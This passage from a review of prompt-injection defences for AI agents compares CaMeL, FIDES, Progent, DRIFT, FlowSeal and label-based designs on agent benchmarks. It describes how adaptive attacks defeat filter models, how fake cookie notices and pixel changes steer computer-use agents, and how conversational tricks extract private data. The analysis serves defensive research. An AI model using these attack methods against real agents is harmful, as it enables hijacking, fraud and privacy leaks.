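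CaMeL completed none of these tasks with any of the four models in the main comparison. It also allowed no attacks, but so would a system that took no actions. With no defence, the three stronger models (GPT-4o, Gemini 2.5 Pro and Claude Sonnet 3.5) completed 52% to 60% of the tasks, and 12% to 38% of attacks succeeded. Two defences that can adjust their rules during a task completed more tasks than CaMeL. Progent, which updates the agent's permissions as it works, completed 7% to 25% with those models. DRIFT, which starts from a plan but has a validator that can approve departures from it, completed 30% to 37% and allowed 1% to 3% of attacks.

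The best compromise in the main comparison was Meta SecAlign, a version of the open model Llama 3.3 70B that Meta trained to disregard instructions in data. It had no outside enforcement and completed 55% of the tasks, but 9% of attacks succeeded. That rate may be tolerable for a shopping assistant, but hardly for an agent that makes frequent bank transfers.

CaMeL's score of zero on AgentDyn probably reflects a real difficulty with unexpected situations, but it may exaggerate the problem. CaMeL's planner writes code to handle a tool's output before seeing any, so it needs to know the output's format. Peters-Gill and colleagues found that they had to add these formats to the tool descriptions to get reasonable results on two benchmarks, and that the original CaMeL tests had needed the same addition. Without them, CaMeL would do badly on a new set of tools for a reason that documentation could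 fix. The AgentDyn team also told every agent to finish its task without asking the user for confirmation, because agents kept stopping to ask. That is reasonable for an automated test, but CaMeL relies on asking the user when a policy blocks a call.

This test did not include FIDES. FIDES chooses one step at a time, so it could in principle respond to the request for a code. But the request comes from outside, and once the planner reads it in full, its context remains untrusted. FIDES would have to learn what the page requires through an answer of a fixed type, such as a choice from a list that includes "enter a code from email", and its policy would then have to allow a payment.

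AgentDyn is also more realistic about where attackers can write. One AgentDojo attack sits in the main text of a harmless person's own website, while AgentDyn confines its web attacks to ads. When the attack is only in an ad, a system that gives the whole page one label must still distrust all of it. If the system could label the ad separately, the planner could keep reading the rest, but somebody would have to write the code that separates them.

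### What a fixed set of attacks can show

AgentDojo and AgentDyn both supply prewritten attacks. One successful attack disproves a claim of complete protection, but a result of zero successful attacks proves much less, because a real attacker can study the defence and try again. Narisetty and colleagues criticise researchers for treating resistance to a known list of attacks as resistance to attackers. In *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026), a filter that blocked every fixed attack on one model let through 28% once the attacks were adapted to it.

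Rewording an email may get it past a filter, but it doesn't change the label that a deterministic check relies on. For FIDES and CaMeL, the fixed attacks are therefore most useful for finding software faults, such as a tool that someone forgot to cover or a label that gets lost as data moves through the system. They are weak evidence of how often an attacker would succeed against a bank's own labels and policies, because the experimenters wrote the ones used in the benchmark.

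Newer models make the security scores even less informative. On AgentDyn, with no defence, the standard attack succeeded in 0.4% of cases against GPT-5-mini, 0.9% against Claude Sonnet 4.5 and 5.0% against GPT-5.1. At 0.4%, a defence has only about two of the 560 cases to prevent. Li and colleagues think developers have probably trained recent models on the standard attack's widely used template, so their main comparison uses older models. When they wrote new attacks to suit each scenario, success rose to 2.1%, 3.0% and 5.6% respectively, though they concede that these attacks are still weak.

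Utility scores are more reliable, because measuring them doesn't require guessing what an attacker would try. But the newest models in these experiments, such as GPT-5.2, are well behind the best now available, and no published run here combines a current frontier model, tasks that change, and labels that someone assigned before seeing the attacks.

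## Attack experiments: what still gets through

Attacks designed by someone who has studied a defence are much harder to stop than prewritten emails. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested twelve published defences against such attacks. The original papers reported attack success close to zero for most of the defences, but in the new tests most failed against more than 90% of attacks. All twelve depend on a model to notice or resist hostile text, and none uses labels or separates a planner from a reader, so the results matter most for gatekeepers that are themselves models.

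### Twelve defences, attacked again

Each attack is a loop that proposes some text, scores how close it came to succeeding, and uses the best candidates to propose better ones. Nasr and colleagues ran this loop with gradients computed from a model's internals, with reinforcement learning, with a search in which a language model rewrites promising candidates, and with people. More than 500 people took part in an online competition. The researchers gave the automated attacks plenty of computing power to find out whether a defence could be broken at all.

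Two of the twelve defend against jailbreaks, where the user is the attacker. The other ten defend against prompt injection, and nine of those have a comparable attack success rate:

| Defence | How it works | Success of adapted attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Uses markers to separate trusted from untrusted text | Above 95% |
| Prompt Sandwiching | Repeats the user's request after the untrusted text | Above 95% |
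| StruQ | Trains the model on examples of attacks | 100% |
| Meta SecAlign | Trains the model on examples of attacks | 96% |
| Protect AI Detector, PromptGuard, Model Armor | A separate model screens the text | Above 90% |
| PIGuard | A separate model screens the text | 71% |
| MELON | Runs the agent again without the user's request and compares the tool calls | 76%, or 95% if the attacker knows the design |

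The tests used different benchmarks, so the table doesn't rank the defences. Meta SecAlign seemed the best compromise on AgentDyn, where 9% of attacks succeeded against it, but the table makes that result less reassuring. On AgentDojo, the reported attack success rate against it was 2% for fixed attacks and 96% for a search adapted to the defence.

On a selected set of scenarios, the automated search succeeded in 69%, while the human attackers collectively succeeded in all of them. One success among hundreds of people was enough for a scenario to count, but a real mailbox is similarly exposed to everyone who knows its address.

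### A gatekeeper that reads the attack

A model that filters text has to read what the attacker wrote, so the attacker can try to write one text that both gets past the filter and persuades the agent. Nasr and colleagues found such texts for every filter they tried, including several filters combined. Many of these texts looked like ordinary office procedure, and a filter strict enough to stop them would also stop a lot of genuine notes.

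The automated search received each filter's confidence score, which a hospital would never publish. Not having the scores would slow an attacker down, but people with limited feedback still produced 123 successful injections against the filters in the strictest setting. An attacker can also practise on a copy if the hospital uses a filter that anyone can download or rent.

Studying a defence is also getting easier. *Locks Tested Without Burglars* describes AI coding assistants that read a defence's source code, found its hidden prompts and assumptions, and wrote attacks tailored to them. They raised attack success by up to 50–60% on three defences, including DRIFT, which had allowed only 1% to 3% of attacks on AgentDyn.

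Attackers also succeed more often when they can try repeatedly. Narisetty and colleagues cite tests of Claude Opus 4.5 as a coding agent, in which adaptive attacks succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. If every attempt had an independent 4.7% chance, the rates would be 38% with ten attempts and 99% with a hundred. The real rates rise more slowly, presumably because some scenarios are much harder than others, but they are still far too high for an agent that can move money. Newer models do better. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) cites OpenAI's report that GPT-5.6 Sol had a sixth as many injection failures as a production model from four months earlier.

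Nasr and colleagues still think filters are worth having, because they are easy to install and stop unsophisticated attacks. The harm a filter's mistake can do depends on what else protects the data. If a small local model alone decides which patient records may leave the hospital, an attacker who fools it gets the records. Ordinary code can prevent this by first removing every record that may not leave, so that the same mistake only produces a worse answer.

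### Progent under an adapted attack

Five of the fourteen people who wrote *The Attacker Moves Second* also worked on CaMeL, and the paper did not attack CaMeL or any similar design. Narisetty and colleagues began to fill that gap in June 2026 by testing Progent.

Progent checks each tool call against privilege rules, which specify the tools an agent may use and with what arguments. Ordinary code applies the rules, but a language model writes them from the user's request and can change them after reading what the tools return. Ma and colleagues point out that Progent calls this helper model at every step. The helper is the obvious weak point, so the adapted attack tried to get it to widen the rules by presenting the harmful action as a routine step that somebody had already approved.

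The test used Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, as both agent and helper. It paired the first eight user tasks in each of three AgentDojo suites with every injection task, and the researchers ran everything three times. The table gives attack success in per cent.

| Suite | No defence | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adapted attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0 | 1.9 | 3.7 |
| Slack | 58.3 | 10.8 | 4.2 |
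| Workspace | 0.0 | 0.0 | 0.0 |
| Average | 25.8 | 4.2 | 2.6 |

This is encouraging but weak evidence. Progent did not cause the Workspace zeros, since the small model ignored the injected instructions even with no defence. Without that suite, the averages are about 39%, 6% and 4%. The adapted attack also did worse overall than the standard one. Narisetty and colleagues suggest that making the instruction sound harmless to the helper also made the agent less likely to obey it, in which case the 2.6% is partly due to a poor attack.

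They tried a single handwritten template and did not use the kind of automated search that broke the twelve earlier defences. They also work for LaunchSafe, a security firm that builds its products on this approach. Progent's developers had reported a similar range, 0.5% to 4.2%, for their adapted attacks on GPT-4o, but they too have a stake in the result. With Progent, the agent completed 27.1% of its tasks under the standard attack, down from 45.2% without it, and each task took about 15 times as many model calls.

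*INFUSE* (2026) got a much less favourable result when it tested versions of Progent and CaMeL rebuilt for the command shell, where an agent types commands to the operating system. Across five models, with 200 attack-task pairs per model, nine of the ten comparisons showed no clear difference from having no defence. Progent also cut utility by 64% to 75% on three of the four models whose utility was measured. *INFUSE* limits its conclusion to its own adaptations. A likely explanation for the weak results is that the shell is a single tool that can do almost anything, so a rule about which tools the agent may use does little to restrict it.

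A fixed set of attacks can also miss a known vulnerability. Peters-Gill and colleagues extended AgentDojo to groups of agents that call one another. Attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time with no defence, 0.2% when each agent ran CaMeL separately, and never with multi-CaMeL. The same researchers had built an attack that carried a planted command from one separate CaMeL agent into the next agent's instructions, so the 0.2% alone makes that setup look safer than it is.

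Narisetty and colleagues would like to see one further experiment, in which the attack uses only actions the agent is already allowed to take. Designs based on labels and fixed plans permit several such attacks.

### False observations and an approved plan

In branch steering, an attacker gives an agent false observations so that it takes a harmful branch of an approved plan. The fake review that triggers a hotel booking is a simple case. The problem is worse for agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking. Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (January 2026) studied branch steering in these agents.

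They adapted CaMeL to such agents. The planner writes a complete program without seeing the screen. While the program runs, a quarantined vision model looks at screenshots and answers questions such as whether a cookie notice is showing or where a button is. Since the planner can't see what happens, it has to allow for many possibilities. An average plan had 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with 5 calls and 4 branches for CaMeL on AgentDojo. About half the steps in a plan were fallbacks that a given run never used.

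The design works better than one might expect, but the paper is generous in reporting that it keeps up to 57% of a frontier model's performance. Claude Sonnet 4.5 had completed 109 tasks without isolation. The isolated agent completed 62 of these (57%) when it had five attempts at each and any success counted, but only 31 (28%) on the first attempt. A user who can't tell which of five attempts worked should expect a result closer to 28%.

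Foerster and colleagues demonstrated two ways to steer an agent. In one, an advertisement imitates a cookie notice. Almost every browsing plan includes a step for dismissing such notices, so the agent clicks on the advertisement and lands on the attacker's site. In the other, small changes to an advertisement's pixels make the vision model report the wrong location and give a plausible reason. On a medicines website, this sent the agent to a particular drug instead of the category page the user wanted. The planner never read anything hostile, and the agent took only actions in its plan.

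Stricter policies are hard to write for clicks. A rule can stop an email to a stranger because the recipient is an argument of the call, but a click specifies only a position on the screen. Clicking the same position may log the user in on one page and delete a file on another. The researchers therefore left out CaMeL's policies and tried redundancy.

The first check compared what the vision model reported with the page's underlying structure. It caught the fake notice in one common advertising format but missed it in another that lets advertisers supply their own page code. The second check used an independent vision model, which could not reliably separate fake notices from real ones without disrupting ordinary tasks. The pixel attack got past this check even at a setting that raised many false alarms. The isolated agent used 1.88 times as many tokens as an unprotected one, and the second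 check raised that to 6.57 times.

These demonstrations cover only a few pages, so they don't show how often steering would succeed across the web. The attacker is also assumed to know the user's task and roughly predict the plan, and the pixel attack relied on access to the internals of a 7-billion-parameter vision model. The fake notice is more worrying because it needs no such access. Isolation still limits the damage, because the attacker can only use actions in the plan. Steering a bank transfer would probably take several false answers that fit together.

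Foerster and colleagues also built a version of FIDES that lets the planner open yes-or-no answers and stops after 70 calls. This limits the information that reaches the planner to about 70 bits. The original FIDES does not keep a running total. The new agent was about as capable as the CaMeL version, but it used 29.6 times as many tokens as an unprotected agent because the planner reread the whole history at every step.

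### Summaries that mislead

A text-to-text attack corrupts a summary or an answer without changing any of the agent's actions, and the harm comes when a person relies on that text. Suppose a manager asks an agent to compare three suppliers, and one supplier has planted false claims in a document that the agent reads. The agent fetches the right files, sends the summary to the right person and passes every check, but the manager relies on the corrupted summary and signs the wrong contract.

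Narisetty and colleagues note that CaMeL explicitly does not try to prevent this. The same gap explains some of the odd failures on AgentDojo. Garby and colleagues report that CaMeL, FIDES and the system that checks Scala code were each marked as having allowed a "successful attack" in the travel suite because the agent had quoted hotel reviews and the scoring code found the attacker's recommendation in the quotations. It isn't obvious that this should count as a failure, since a user who asks about reviews should see what they contain. It would be worse if the agent recommended the hotel as its own advice.

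The labels could help a little here. The system tracks which sources went into a summary, so it could easily show the reader a warning. But nearly every summary of outside material would carry the same warning, and people would soon stop noticing it. Asking a second model for another summary may not help much, because both models would read the same false claims. Reducing the answer to a few typed values would limit what an attacker could say, but it wouldn't give the manager the explanation they asked for.

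### Tasks that put a file in charge

A user who tells an agent to pay the bill in a file gives anyone who can edit that file authority over the payment. This accounts for both of the attacks that got through in the LLMbda experiment's 1,296 runs. Both were the same attack on the same task with GPT-5.2. Each model faced that combination only three times, and the attack succeeded in two of the three runs with GPT-5.2 and in none with the other two models. The overall success rate therefore understates how well the attack worked where it applied.

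Labels can't separate the real bill from the false one, because both come from the same untrusted file, which the user asked the agent to act on. Garby and colleagues call such cases the semantic limit of information-flow defences. They overstate the agreement between systems when they argue that four independent ones ended up with the same remaining failures. The payment file defeated LLMbda and CaMeL, but the failures they cite for FIDES and the Scala system involve quoted hotel reviews, a different problem. These cases also all come from the same benchmark. The conclusion about the payment file is still right, because it follows from the user's request.

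A company can refuse to take important arguments from untrusted sources. *Beyond Instruction Override* (2026) measures the drawbacks of this policy, using attacks that tamper with the user's task instead of replacing it. It ran CaMeL with policies that require values such as the recipient and the amount to come from trusted fields, and compared it with other defenses, including the part of DRIFT that tries to remove injected text before the agent acts on it. The figures are averages over five models.

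| Defence | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL with strict argument policies | 1.3% | 13.3% | 13.9% |
| DRIFT's injection removal | 6.6% | 98.0% | 93.3% |

Few businesses would accept an agent that fails six out of seven tasks, so on these figures most would choose DRIFT over CaMeL. That seems reasonable for low-stakes work. But DRIFT has to judge what the text means, so an attacker who adapts could raise its 6.6% attack success rate a good deal, while rewording alone shouldn't raise CaMeL's 1.3%.

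The usual compromise is to ask the user before the payment goes out. This works if the user can recognise the right account number, but many people would have to look it up, and the obvious place to look is the file that the attacker changed. Phoning the supplier would confirm the number, but it would take several minutes and remove most of the benefit of having an agent. Asking only about new payees would reduce the number of questions and make users less likely to approve without checking. Narisetty and colleagues regard tasks in which untrusted data has to determine an important action as the deepest open problem in the field, because nobody has a principled account of which ones can be made secure.

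### Private data given away in ordinary conversation

In September 2026, Shim and colleagues studied an attacker who tries to get somebody's private data by talking to the agent, whereas the attackers discussed so far wanted to change what the agent does or reports. In their main example, Jane's agent holds information about Mark's mental health, and Mark's former wife tries to get it. The agent and its tools are honest, and there is no injected instruction.

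Shim and colleagues began with a detailed defensive prompt that tells the agent to check who is asking, request consent from the person the data concerns, and wait for a reply. Earlier attacks had extracted only 1.9% to 3.0% of the sensitive items. The researchers noticed that the procedure starts only if the agent recognises a message as a request for information, so they designed three classes of attack to avoid triggering it. They then built FlowSeal, which moves the check outside the conversation. The table gives the share of sensitive items leaked over 105 scenarios, each run three times.

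| Class of attack | Why the agent misses it | Consent prompt | FlowSeal |
|---|---|---|---|
| Collaborative workspace lure | Disclosure looks like a contribution to a shared document | 52.2% | 0.5% |
| Semantic obfuscation | The agent's corrections to a list show which entries are true | 75.6% | 2.3% |
| Channel decoupling | The request comes through one channel and the disclosure goes out through another | 43.8% | 2.2% |

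The second class is an implicit flow, because the agent writes nothing confidential. Another round of automated prompt improvement barely helped, and the second class was still at 69.7%.

FlowSeal labels each sensitive record with its owner, using information such as an email's sender or a document's access list, and tracks which records the agent has read. When the agent tries to write or share something, ordinary code checks the destination. It allows recipients the owner has approved and rejects those the owner has blocked. For any other recipient, if the agent has read records that person isn't authorised to see, the code sends those records and the proposed text to a separate model, which answers only "safe" or "blocked". That model doesn't see the conversation, so the attacker's framing is less likely to mislead it.

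The results depend heavily on this one model. When Shim and colleagues replaced it with a rule that always blocks, the first class of attack obtained 1.3% of the items, but the agent completed none of its legitimate tasks. With a rule that always allows, utility was 79.4% and the leak rate was 24.9%. With the model, utility was 72.4% and the leak rate was 0.5%. Their theorem says that confidential content can't reach an unauthorised destination unless this model makes a mistake. That is a fairly weak guarantee when the model makes so many of the decisions.

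Ordinary code performs the policy checks in FIDES, so Shim and colleagues are mistaken when they say that it leaves enforcement to the language model and would therefore fail against their attacks. A strict FIDES policy would behave much like the rule that always blocks. It would probably stop these leaks, but it would also stop harmless messages to the same people. The zero for legitimate tasks is an extreme case, though, because the test had no approved recipients and the data's owners ignored every request for consent.

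FlowSeal hasn't yet faced an attacker who knows how it works. Its designers aimed their three attacks at consent prompts. The separate model still reads text that an attacker may have influenced, and the designers say it mostly fails on paraphrases. They also describe an attack they didn't test, which splits one fact across several messages that each look harmless.

FlowSeal adds little direct cost. A run cost $0.109 with it and $0.092 without any defence, and the reported time rose by 37%, from 5.44 to 7.45 seconds. Much of the increase comes from agents rewriting blocked messages and trying again, and the measurements were taken under attack, so the increase may be smaller in ordinary use. The times look short for runs of about 50 model calls. If they are average gaps between calls, as in the paper's later live test, a complete run would take about two-thirds longer with FlowSeal than without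 it.

Withholding data that should be shared is probably FlowSeal's larger drawback. In a further test, where the request was legitimate and the owner would agree if asked, agents with the consent prompts shared 61% to 67% of what they should have. The agent with FlowSeal shared only 32.7%, largely because it asked for consent less often. The 72.4% utility figure doesn't reflect this, since none of the tasks behind it required private data.

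Shim and colleagues also tried the second class of attack on real Gmail and Notion accounts. The attack extracted 34.7% of the sensitive items from an agent protected only by a model that advises on each disclosure, and none from an agent with FlowSeal. They counted a leak only if the private fact appeared word for word, so they would have missed the paraphrases that FlowSeal handles worst.

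## Simulations and measurements of how labels spread

Label creep can make an agent useless without any attack, because restrictive labels spread until they block ordinary work. Researchers have simulated this spread, tried to measure which inputs actually influence an output, and built agents that limit the spread. In nearly all of this work, they distrust the model because hostile text might hijack it, not because it might have goals of its own.

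### One web page and its consequences

Suppose a shop manager asks an agent to check a supplier's delivery times, update the stock sheet and email the warehouse. The agent runs in an ordinary loop, and every label is T (trusted) or U (untrusted).

| Step | What the agent does | Label of the new text | Label of the context afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Receives the manager's request | T | T |
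| 2 | Reads the stock sheet | T | T |
| 3 | Reads the supplier's web page | U | U |
| 4 | Looks up the warehouse in the staff directory | U, because an untrusted context made the call | U |
| 5 | Updates the stock sheet | U | U |
| 6 | Reads the stock sheet the next day, in a new conversation | U | U |

From step 3 on, a policy that requires a trusted context blocks the email to the warehouse, even if the page contains only delivery times. If the policy allows the update in step 5, the stock sheet carries the label into the next day's work. FIDES avoids some of this by hiding restricted results in variables, but the label spreads once the planner has to open one.

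*APPA* proves that each change to a label must remove at least one permitted reader or lower the level of trust, which limits the spread. With ten readers and two levels of trust, a label can become stricter at most 11 times. This limit is not very reassuring, because after 11 changes no one is permitted to read the text.

*Autonomous LLM Agent Worms* (2026) explains that no general procedure can decide whether text a model has read influenced its later decisions. A cautious system therefore doesn't try to identify and ignore web pages that made no difference, though doing so would be better. The paper treats everything the model writes after reading tainted text as tainted, and allows only a procedure outside the model to clear it, because a hijacked model could otherwise clear its own output.

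### Twenty tool calls in ten layouts

Dividing the work among several agents might slow the spread of labels, since what one agent reads need not taint the others. Gregory, Domico and colleagues at the University of Wisconsin–Madison tested this idea in a simulation that used no language model (*The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, November 2026).

Each simulated task was a random graph of 20 tool calls, with an arrow wherever one call needed another's result. In the basic setup, the calls were split randomly among five agents. Some calls introduced a high-sensitivity label, and any agent exposed to this label kept it for the rest of the task. Results could travel only along links between agents. If two agents had no direct link, other agents relayed the result between them and picked up its label.

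The ten layouts were a mesh (every pair linked), a star (everything goes through a central agent), a ring, a hierarchy, five random networks, and an ideal layout with links only where the task needed them. For each layout, the researchers calculated

loss = calls that introduce or carry the high label / all calls

excess loss = loss − loss in the ideal layout.

With four sensitive calls out of 20, the excess loss was about 5 percentage points for the star, 4 for the hierarchy and 3 for the ring. The mesh did as well as the ideal layout. The star did worst because its central agent, after forwarding one sensitive result, adds the label to everything it forwards later.

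Networks with higher density, the share of possible links that a network has, nearly always had lower losses. The Spearman correlation between density and loss, which compares rankings, was −0.96 across nine layouts. This excludes the ideal layout, because it changes with every task.

Someone has to monitor every link, so denser networks take more work to monitor. A mesh of n agents has n(n − 1)/2 links, which is 10 for five agents and 190 for 20. Using more agents reduced the loss but added links. Gregory and colleagues suggest a sparser random network as a compromise, because one that includes each possible link with probability 0.3 has 70% fewer links than a mesh on average. But they discarded networks that left any agent cut off, and the five-agent network they tested had 7 of the 10 possible links, only 30% fewer than a mesh.

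Assigning the sensitive tools to a few agents, such as a dedicated banking agent, also lowered the loss in every layout and needed no extra links.

Gregory and colleagues conclude that layout alone cannot prevent the loss, so agents also need a safe way to remove labels. The conclusion is right, but their assumptions nearly guarantee it. Labels never come off in the simulation, and if four of 20 calls are sensitive, the loss is at least 20% in any layout. The sizes of the losses are more informative, because with four sensitive calls even the worst layout adds only about one lost call per task, or five percentage points.

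The loss is also only a rough measure of lost work. It counts every call with a high label, including calls that a sensible policy would allow, such as reading a confidential file for someone entitled to see it. The simulation probably makes the mesh look better than it would be in practice, because the mesh's extra links carry nothing unless the task needs them, whereas real agents might use them to share more than necessary.

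### Answering again from what mattered

A better layout keeps the conservative rule. In *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024) tested a less conservative method, which regenerates an answer from only the inputs that influenced it.

For example, if an untrusted newsletter was irrelevant to the question of when the board meets, the system can answer the question again without the newsletter and label the new answer T.

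Siddiqui and colleagues tested two variants. One adds retrieved passages to the prompt, and the other uses a k-nearest-neighbour language model, which adjusts its next-word predictions using similar passages from a store. The version of their paper published in 2025 reports that, in an agent test, the method gave a more permissive label than a baseline in over 85% of cases. The baseline was a model asked to predict the right label by introspection, so the figure doesn't show how often the method improves on simply joining the labels of all the inputs.

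Mistakes in this method mostly harm the answer rather than the label. If the method drops a relevant message, the second answer may be wrong, but the model cannot quote text it never received. With ten messages, the choice of which to keep can still leak up to 10 bits, because there are 2¹⁰ = 1,024 possible subsets. The system also has to generate the answer twice.

### Estimating influence from attention

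*Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, 2026) presents a tool that keeps the model's first answer and estimates which inputs the model used to produce it. Most language models are transformers, in which information moves from one word's position to another only through attention. Each model has many attention heads, which assign weights to earlier positions. The tool runs the prompt and the finished output through the model once and records how much weight every head gave to each input. A simple classifier, trained on labelled examples, then predicts from these weights which inputs the model used.

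Xu and colleagues prove that, to a first approximation, an input cannot affect the output if no later position attends to it. In practice, models attend at least slightly to every input, and a low attention weight does not rule out an effect. In one constructed example, a head gives an input a weight of about two billionths, but a different value for that input would draw nearly all the head's attention and change the output. The input affects the output by being ignored, much as an untaken branch in CaMeL leaks a secret by not running. None of the real flows in the main data set had attention weights nearly that low.

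Sightline's guarantee is therefore statistical. The researchers take one true flow (an input that the output really used) from each of n groups of software projects and score it with the classifier. To miss at most a share α of true flows, they set the threshold at the k-th lowest score, where

k = ⌊α(n + 1)⌋.

With n = 1,000 and α = 1%, k is 10. A new flow drawn the same way is equally likely to take any of the 1,001 ranks, so its chance of falling below the threshold is at most 10/1,001, or just under 1%.

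On four small open models, Sightline missed about 1% of true flows and removed 44% to 66% of the unnecessary labels. The researchers also replayed 120 turns of an agent under attack in AgentDojo, this time aiming to miss no more than 5% of true flows. Sightline removed half of the unnecessary labels, and a policy like the one in FIDES still blocked all 34 attack calls. With so few calls, the policy's true failure rate could be as high as about 8%.

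The method can also work for a model rented from an outside company. A small open model reads the rented model's prompt and output, and the small model's attention serves as the estimate. In tests where each of the four models stood in for a closed one, this was about as accurate as using that model's own attention. A hospital could run the small model on its own machines. However, a hostile rented model might encode a secret in a way that the small model doesn't detect.

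An error here directly weakens the guarantee. If Sightline misses a flow, it removes a label that should have stayed, and the policy check may then allow a forbidden call. Small error rates also add up. If a label has to survive 20 steps and each step independently loses it 1% of the time, the chance of losing it somewhere is

1 − 0.99²⁰ ≈ 18%.

At 5% per step, it is about 64%.

The bigger weakness is the assumption that new flows resemble the ones used for calibration. Attackers choose their own text, so they can look for wording that influences the model but gets a low score, much as adaptive attackers did against filters. None of the paper's six experiments includes such an attacker.

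### Auditing after the run

NeuroTaint, described by Cai, Wen and Tang (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, estimates influence only after the agent has finished. It builds a graph of where data entered, which tools and memories it passed through, and where it had an effect. For each sensitive call, it then looks for traces of the source in the call's arguments:

1. It checks for a unique tag that it added to the source text.
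2. It looks for shared sequences of characters.
3. It compares the meaning of the two texts, to catch paraphrases.
4. It repeats that comparison for small parts of a long source.

If it finds nothing, it uses a language model to judge whether the agent would have made the same call with neutral content in the source. This last step can catch implicit flows.

In 400 test scenarios, 200 of which contained a flow, NeuroTaint found 187 of the flows (93.5% recall) and raised 16 false alarms (92.1% precision). Most of the misses involved text that the agent had paraphrased several times or retrieved from memory.

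The paper reports much worse results for FIDES, with 92 misses and 106 false alarms, but these are weak evidence about the actual design. Forty of the misses came from four software frameworks in which the FIDES baseline flagged nothing, which looks like a fault in the adaptation. The baseline also lost its labels between sessions, whereas FIDES as designed keeps them on stored data. The false alarms are less surprising, since a conservative system is supposed to flag every possible flow.

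NeuroTaint's recall fell to 54.7% when Claude Opus 4.6 ran the agent. At least part of the drop occurred because the benchmark counted a miss when the stronger model refused to make the final call, even though there was then no flow to find.

NeuroTaint analyzes logs after the fact, so its errors don't let attacks through. A miss leaves a gap in the investigation, and a false alarm wastes a reviewer's time. Using the same estimates to approve payments would be a mistake, because they miss 13 in 200 (6.5%) even before an attacker adapts.

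### Sound labels and useful labels

If the conservative rule blocks a harmless email, the user notices and can ask for an exception. But if an estimate wrongly removes a label, the forbidden call goes ahead and nothing unusual appears in the log. Companies will therefore hear much more about harmless actions being blocked, which may push them towards estimates that are too permissive.

Estimating which inputs affect a model's output may also remove fewer labels than the idea of label creep suggests. In the real software that Xu and colleagues studied, only 12% to 14% of the inputs to a model call had no effect on its output, so even a perfect estimate would have left the other labels in place. An agent's long context probably contains more irrelevant text, so an estimate could remove more labels there. But no estimate can help with an account number from a stranger's invoice, because the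 untrusted label is correct.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* proposes soft labels as a compromise. They record how much information an output carries about each input, so a policy could ignore very small amounts. That seems reasonable for tone or formatting, but much less so for a diagnosis or an approval, where the important information may be a single bit.

For actions that are hard to reverse, the system should rely on the conservative label. An estimate could still help show a person which of many untrusted messages probably led to a blocked call. If the system needs a more permissive label, regenerating the answer is the best of the three methods because its errors mainly reduce the quality of the answer.

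### Containing the taint in a branch

Another approach keeps the conservative rule but limits how far a label spreads. In *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026), a main agent can give a risky page to a sub-agent, whose context then takes the label. The sub-agent returns its result as a labelled value, and if the main model inspects that value, it takes on the label too. Unlike Willison's quarantined model, the sub-agent may use tools, because its label limits what those tools can do after it reads the page.

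*APPA* also works out how a blocked call could go ahead. Further reading cannot lift a restriction on trust or recipients, because reading only adds restrictions. Depending on the reason for the block, there are four possible remedies:

- The agent completes a required earlier step.
- An approver permits this exact call, without changing any label or allowing any later call.
- Trusted code changes the data, for example by removing personal details, or resolves a label that was unknown.
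- The agent makes the call in a temporary child branch, so that the resulting label doesn't reach the parent.

The software searches for a combination that would remove the block and offers it to the agent. Suppose a support agent must read a public bug report and then update an internal database. A child branch reads the report and returns only a ticket number, a severity level and a component name, each in a fixed format. If the company's policy accepts those values as trusted, the parent can still write to the database. Accepting the values is a form of endorsement, because a hijacked child could return the wrong severity level.

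A child branch starts with its parent's label. Otherwise, an agent could easily launder secrets by reading a confidential file and then continuing in a child with a clean label.

*APPA* also checks each call against the label that the context would have after the call. One test tool reads a confidential ledger and emails it to an outsider in a single call. The context is clean before the call, so checking only the current label would allow the ledger to be sent.

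The evaluation covered 6,600 episodes with three models. In the 1,320 episodes protected by the full system, the researchers observed no successful attacks, and utility ranged from 64.2% to 91% depending on the benchmark, model and prompt. On a set of corporate tasks, an agent using GPT-5.6 Luna completed 88% with the full system, 56.5% without child branches, and 35.0% without the suggested remedies, still with no successful attacks. Removing the remedies therefore made the agent less useful, but the checks still kept it safe.

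The rest of the evidence is weaker. The 1,320 episodes repeat only 44 task designs, and the paper's contact author works at a vendor, Archestra. The researchers wrote both the corporate tasks and the policies for the two versions of FIDES they compared with *APPA*. Those versions completed only 36% to 46% of the corporate tasks, but their policies left out several of the rules the tasks tested. On the other benchmark, which the researchers did not create, one version of FIDES completed more tasks than *APPA* when both used DeepSeek, although that version allowed many attacks under one of the two prompts.

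### Labels that last between requests

Many agents keep their results for later requests. In an example from Girrens and Wang (SPA system, August 2026), a user asks an agent on Monday to save the details of an invoice and on Tuesday to pay "the invoice we discussed yesterday". If the invoice contains an attacker's account number, the agent may pay the attacker a day after reading it.

SPA stores each result in three parts: the value, its label and a description. Tuesday's planner sees only the description. Monday's planner wrote that description before any tool ran, so the invoice could not have influenced it. The plan can retrieve the value by reference, along with its original label. A summary of the invoice also keeps the invoice's label. If the plan breaks a rule, SPA stops instead of asking the planner to try again, which avoids a retry leak like the one in CaMeL.

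To test this, Girrens and Wang split the 97 AgentDojo tasks into conversations of two to five requests. When an earlier result was available, later plans retrieved it 95.4% of the time without label checks and 89.9% with them. Hiding the stored values from the planner lowered utility only from 65.9% to 62.5%. Adding the label checks lowered it from 62.5% to 35.3%, mostly because the tasks used untrusted results in actions that required trusted data. SPA would therefore block payment of Tuesday's invoice even if the account number were genuine.

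With checks, the reported attack success rate was 0.2%, or about two successful attacks. AgentDojo had wrongly counted two runs as successes after SPA rejected their plans, so the true rate may be zero. But the attacks aimed to change what the agent did immediately, so they hardly tested whether stored text could cause harm later.

### When a summary replaces the conversation

When a long conversation fills a model's context, the surrounding software asks a model to summarise the earlier part and continues from the summary, a step called compaction. Under the conservative rule, the summary's label is the join of the labels on everything it replaces, so one untrusted web page makes the whole summary untrusted. Before compaction, a system could have removed that page and kept the rest. Summarising trusted and untrusted messages separately would preserve some of the distinction between them.

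Real products can make the opposite mistake. Fei, Fei and colleagues (2026), in *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction*, recorded 1,108 automatic compactions in the coding agents Claude Code and Codex, and in every case the software inserted the summary as a user message. Any later check that trusts user messages will also trust any third-party content in the summary.

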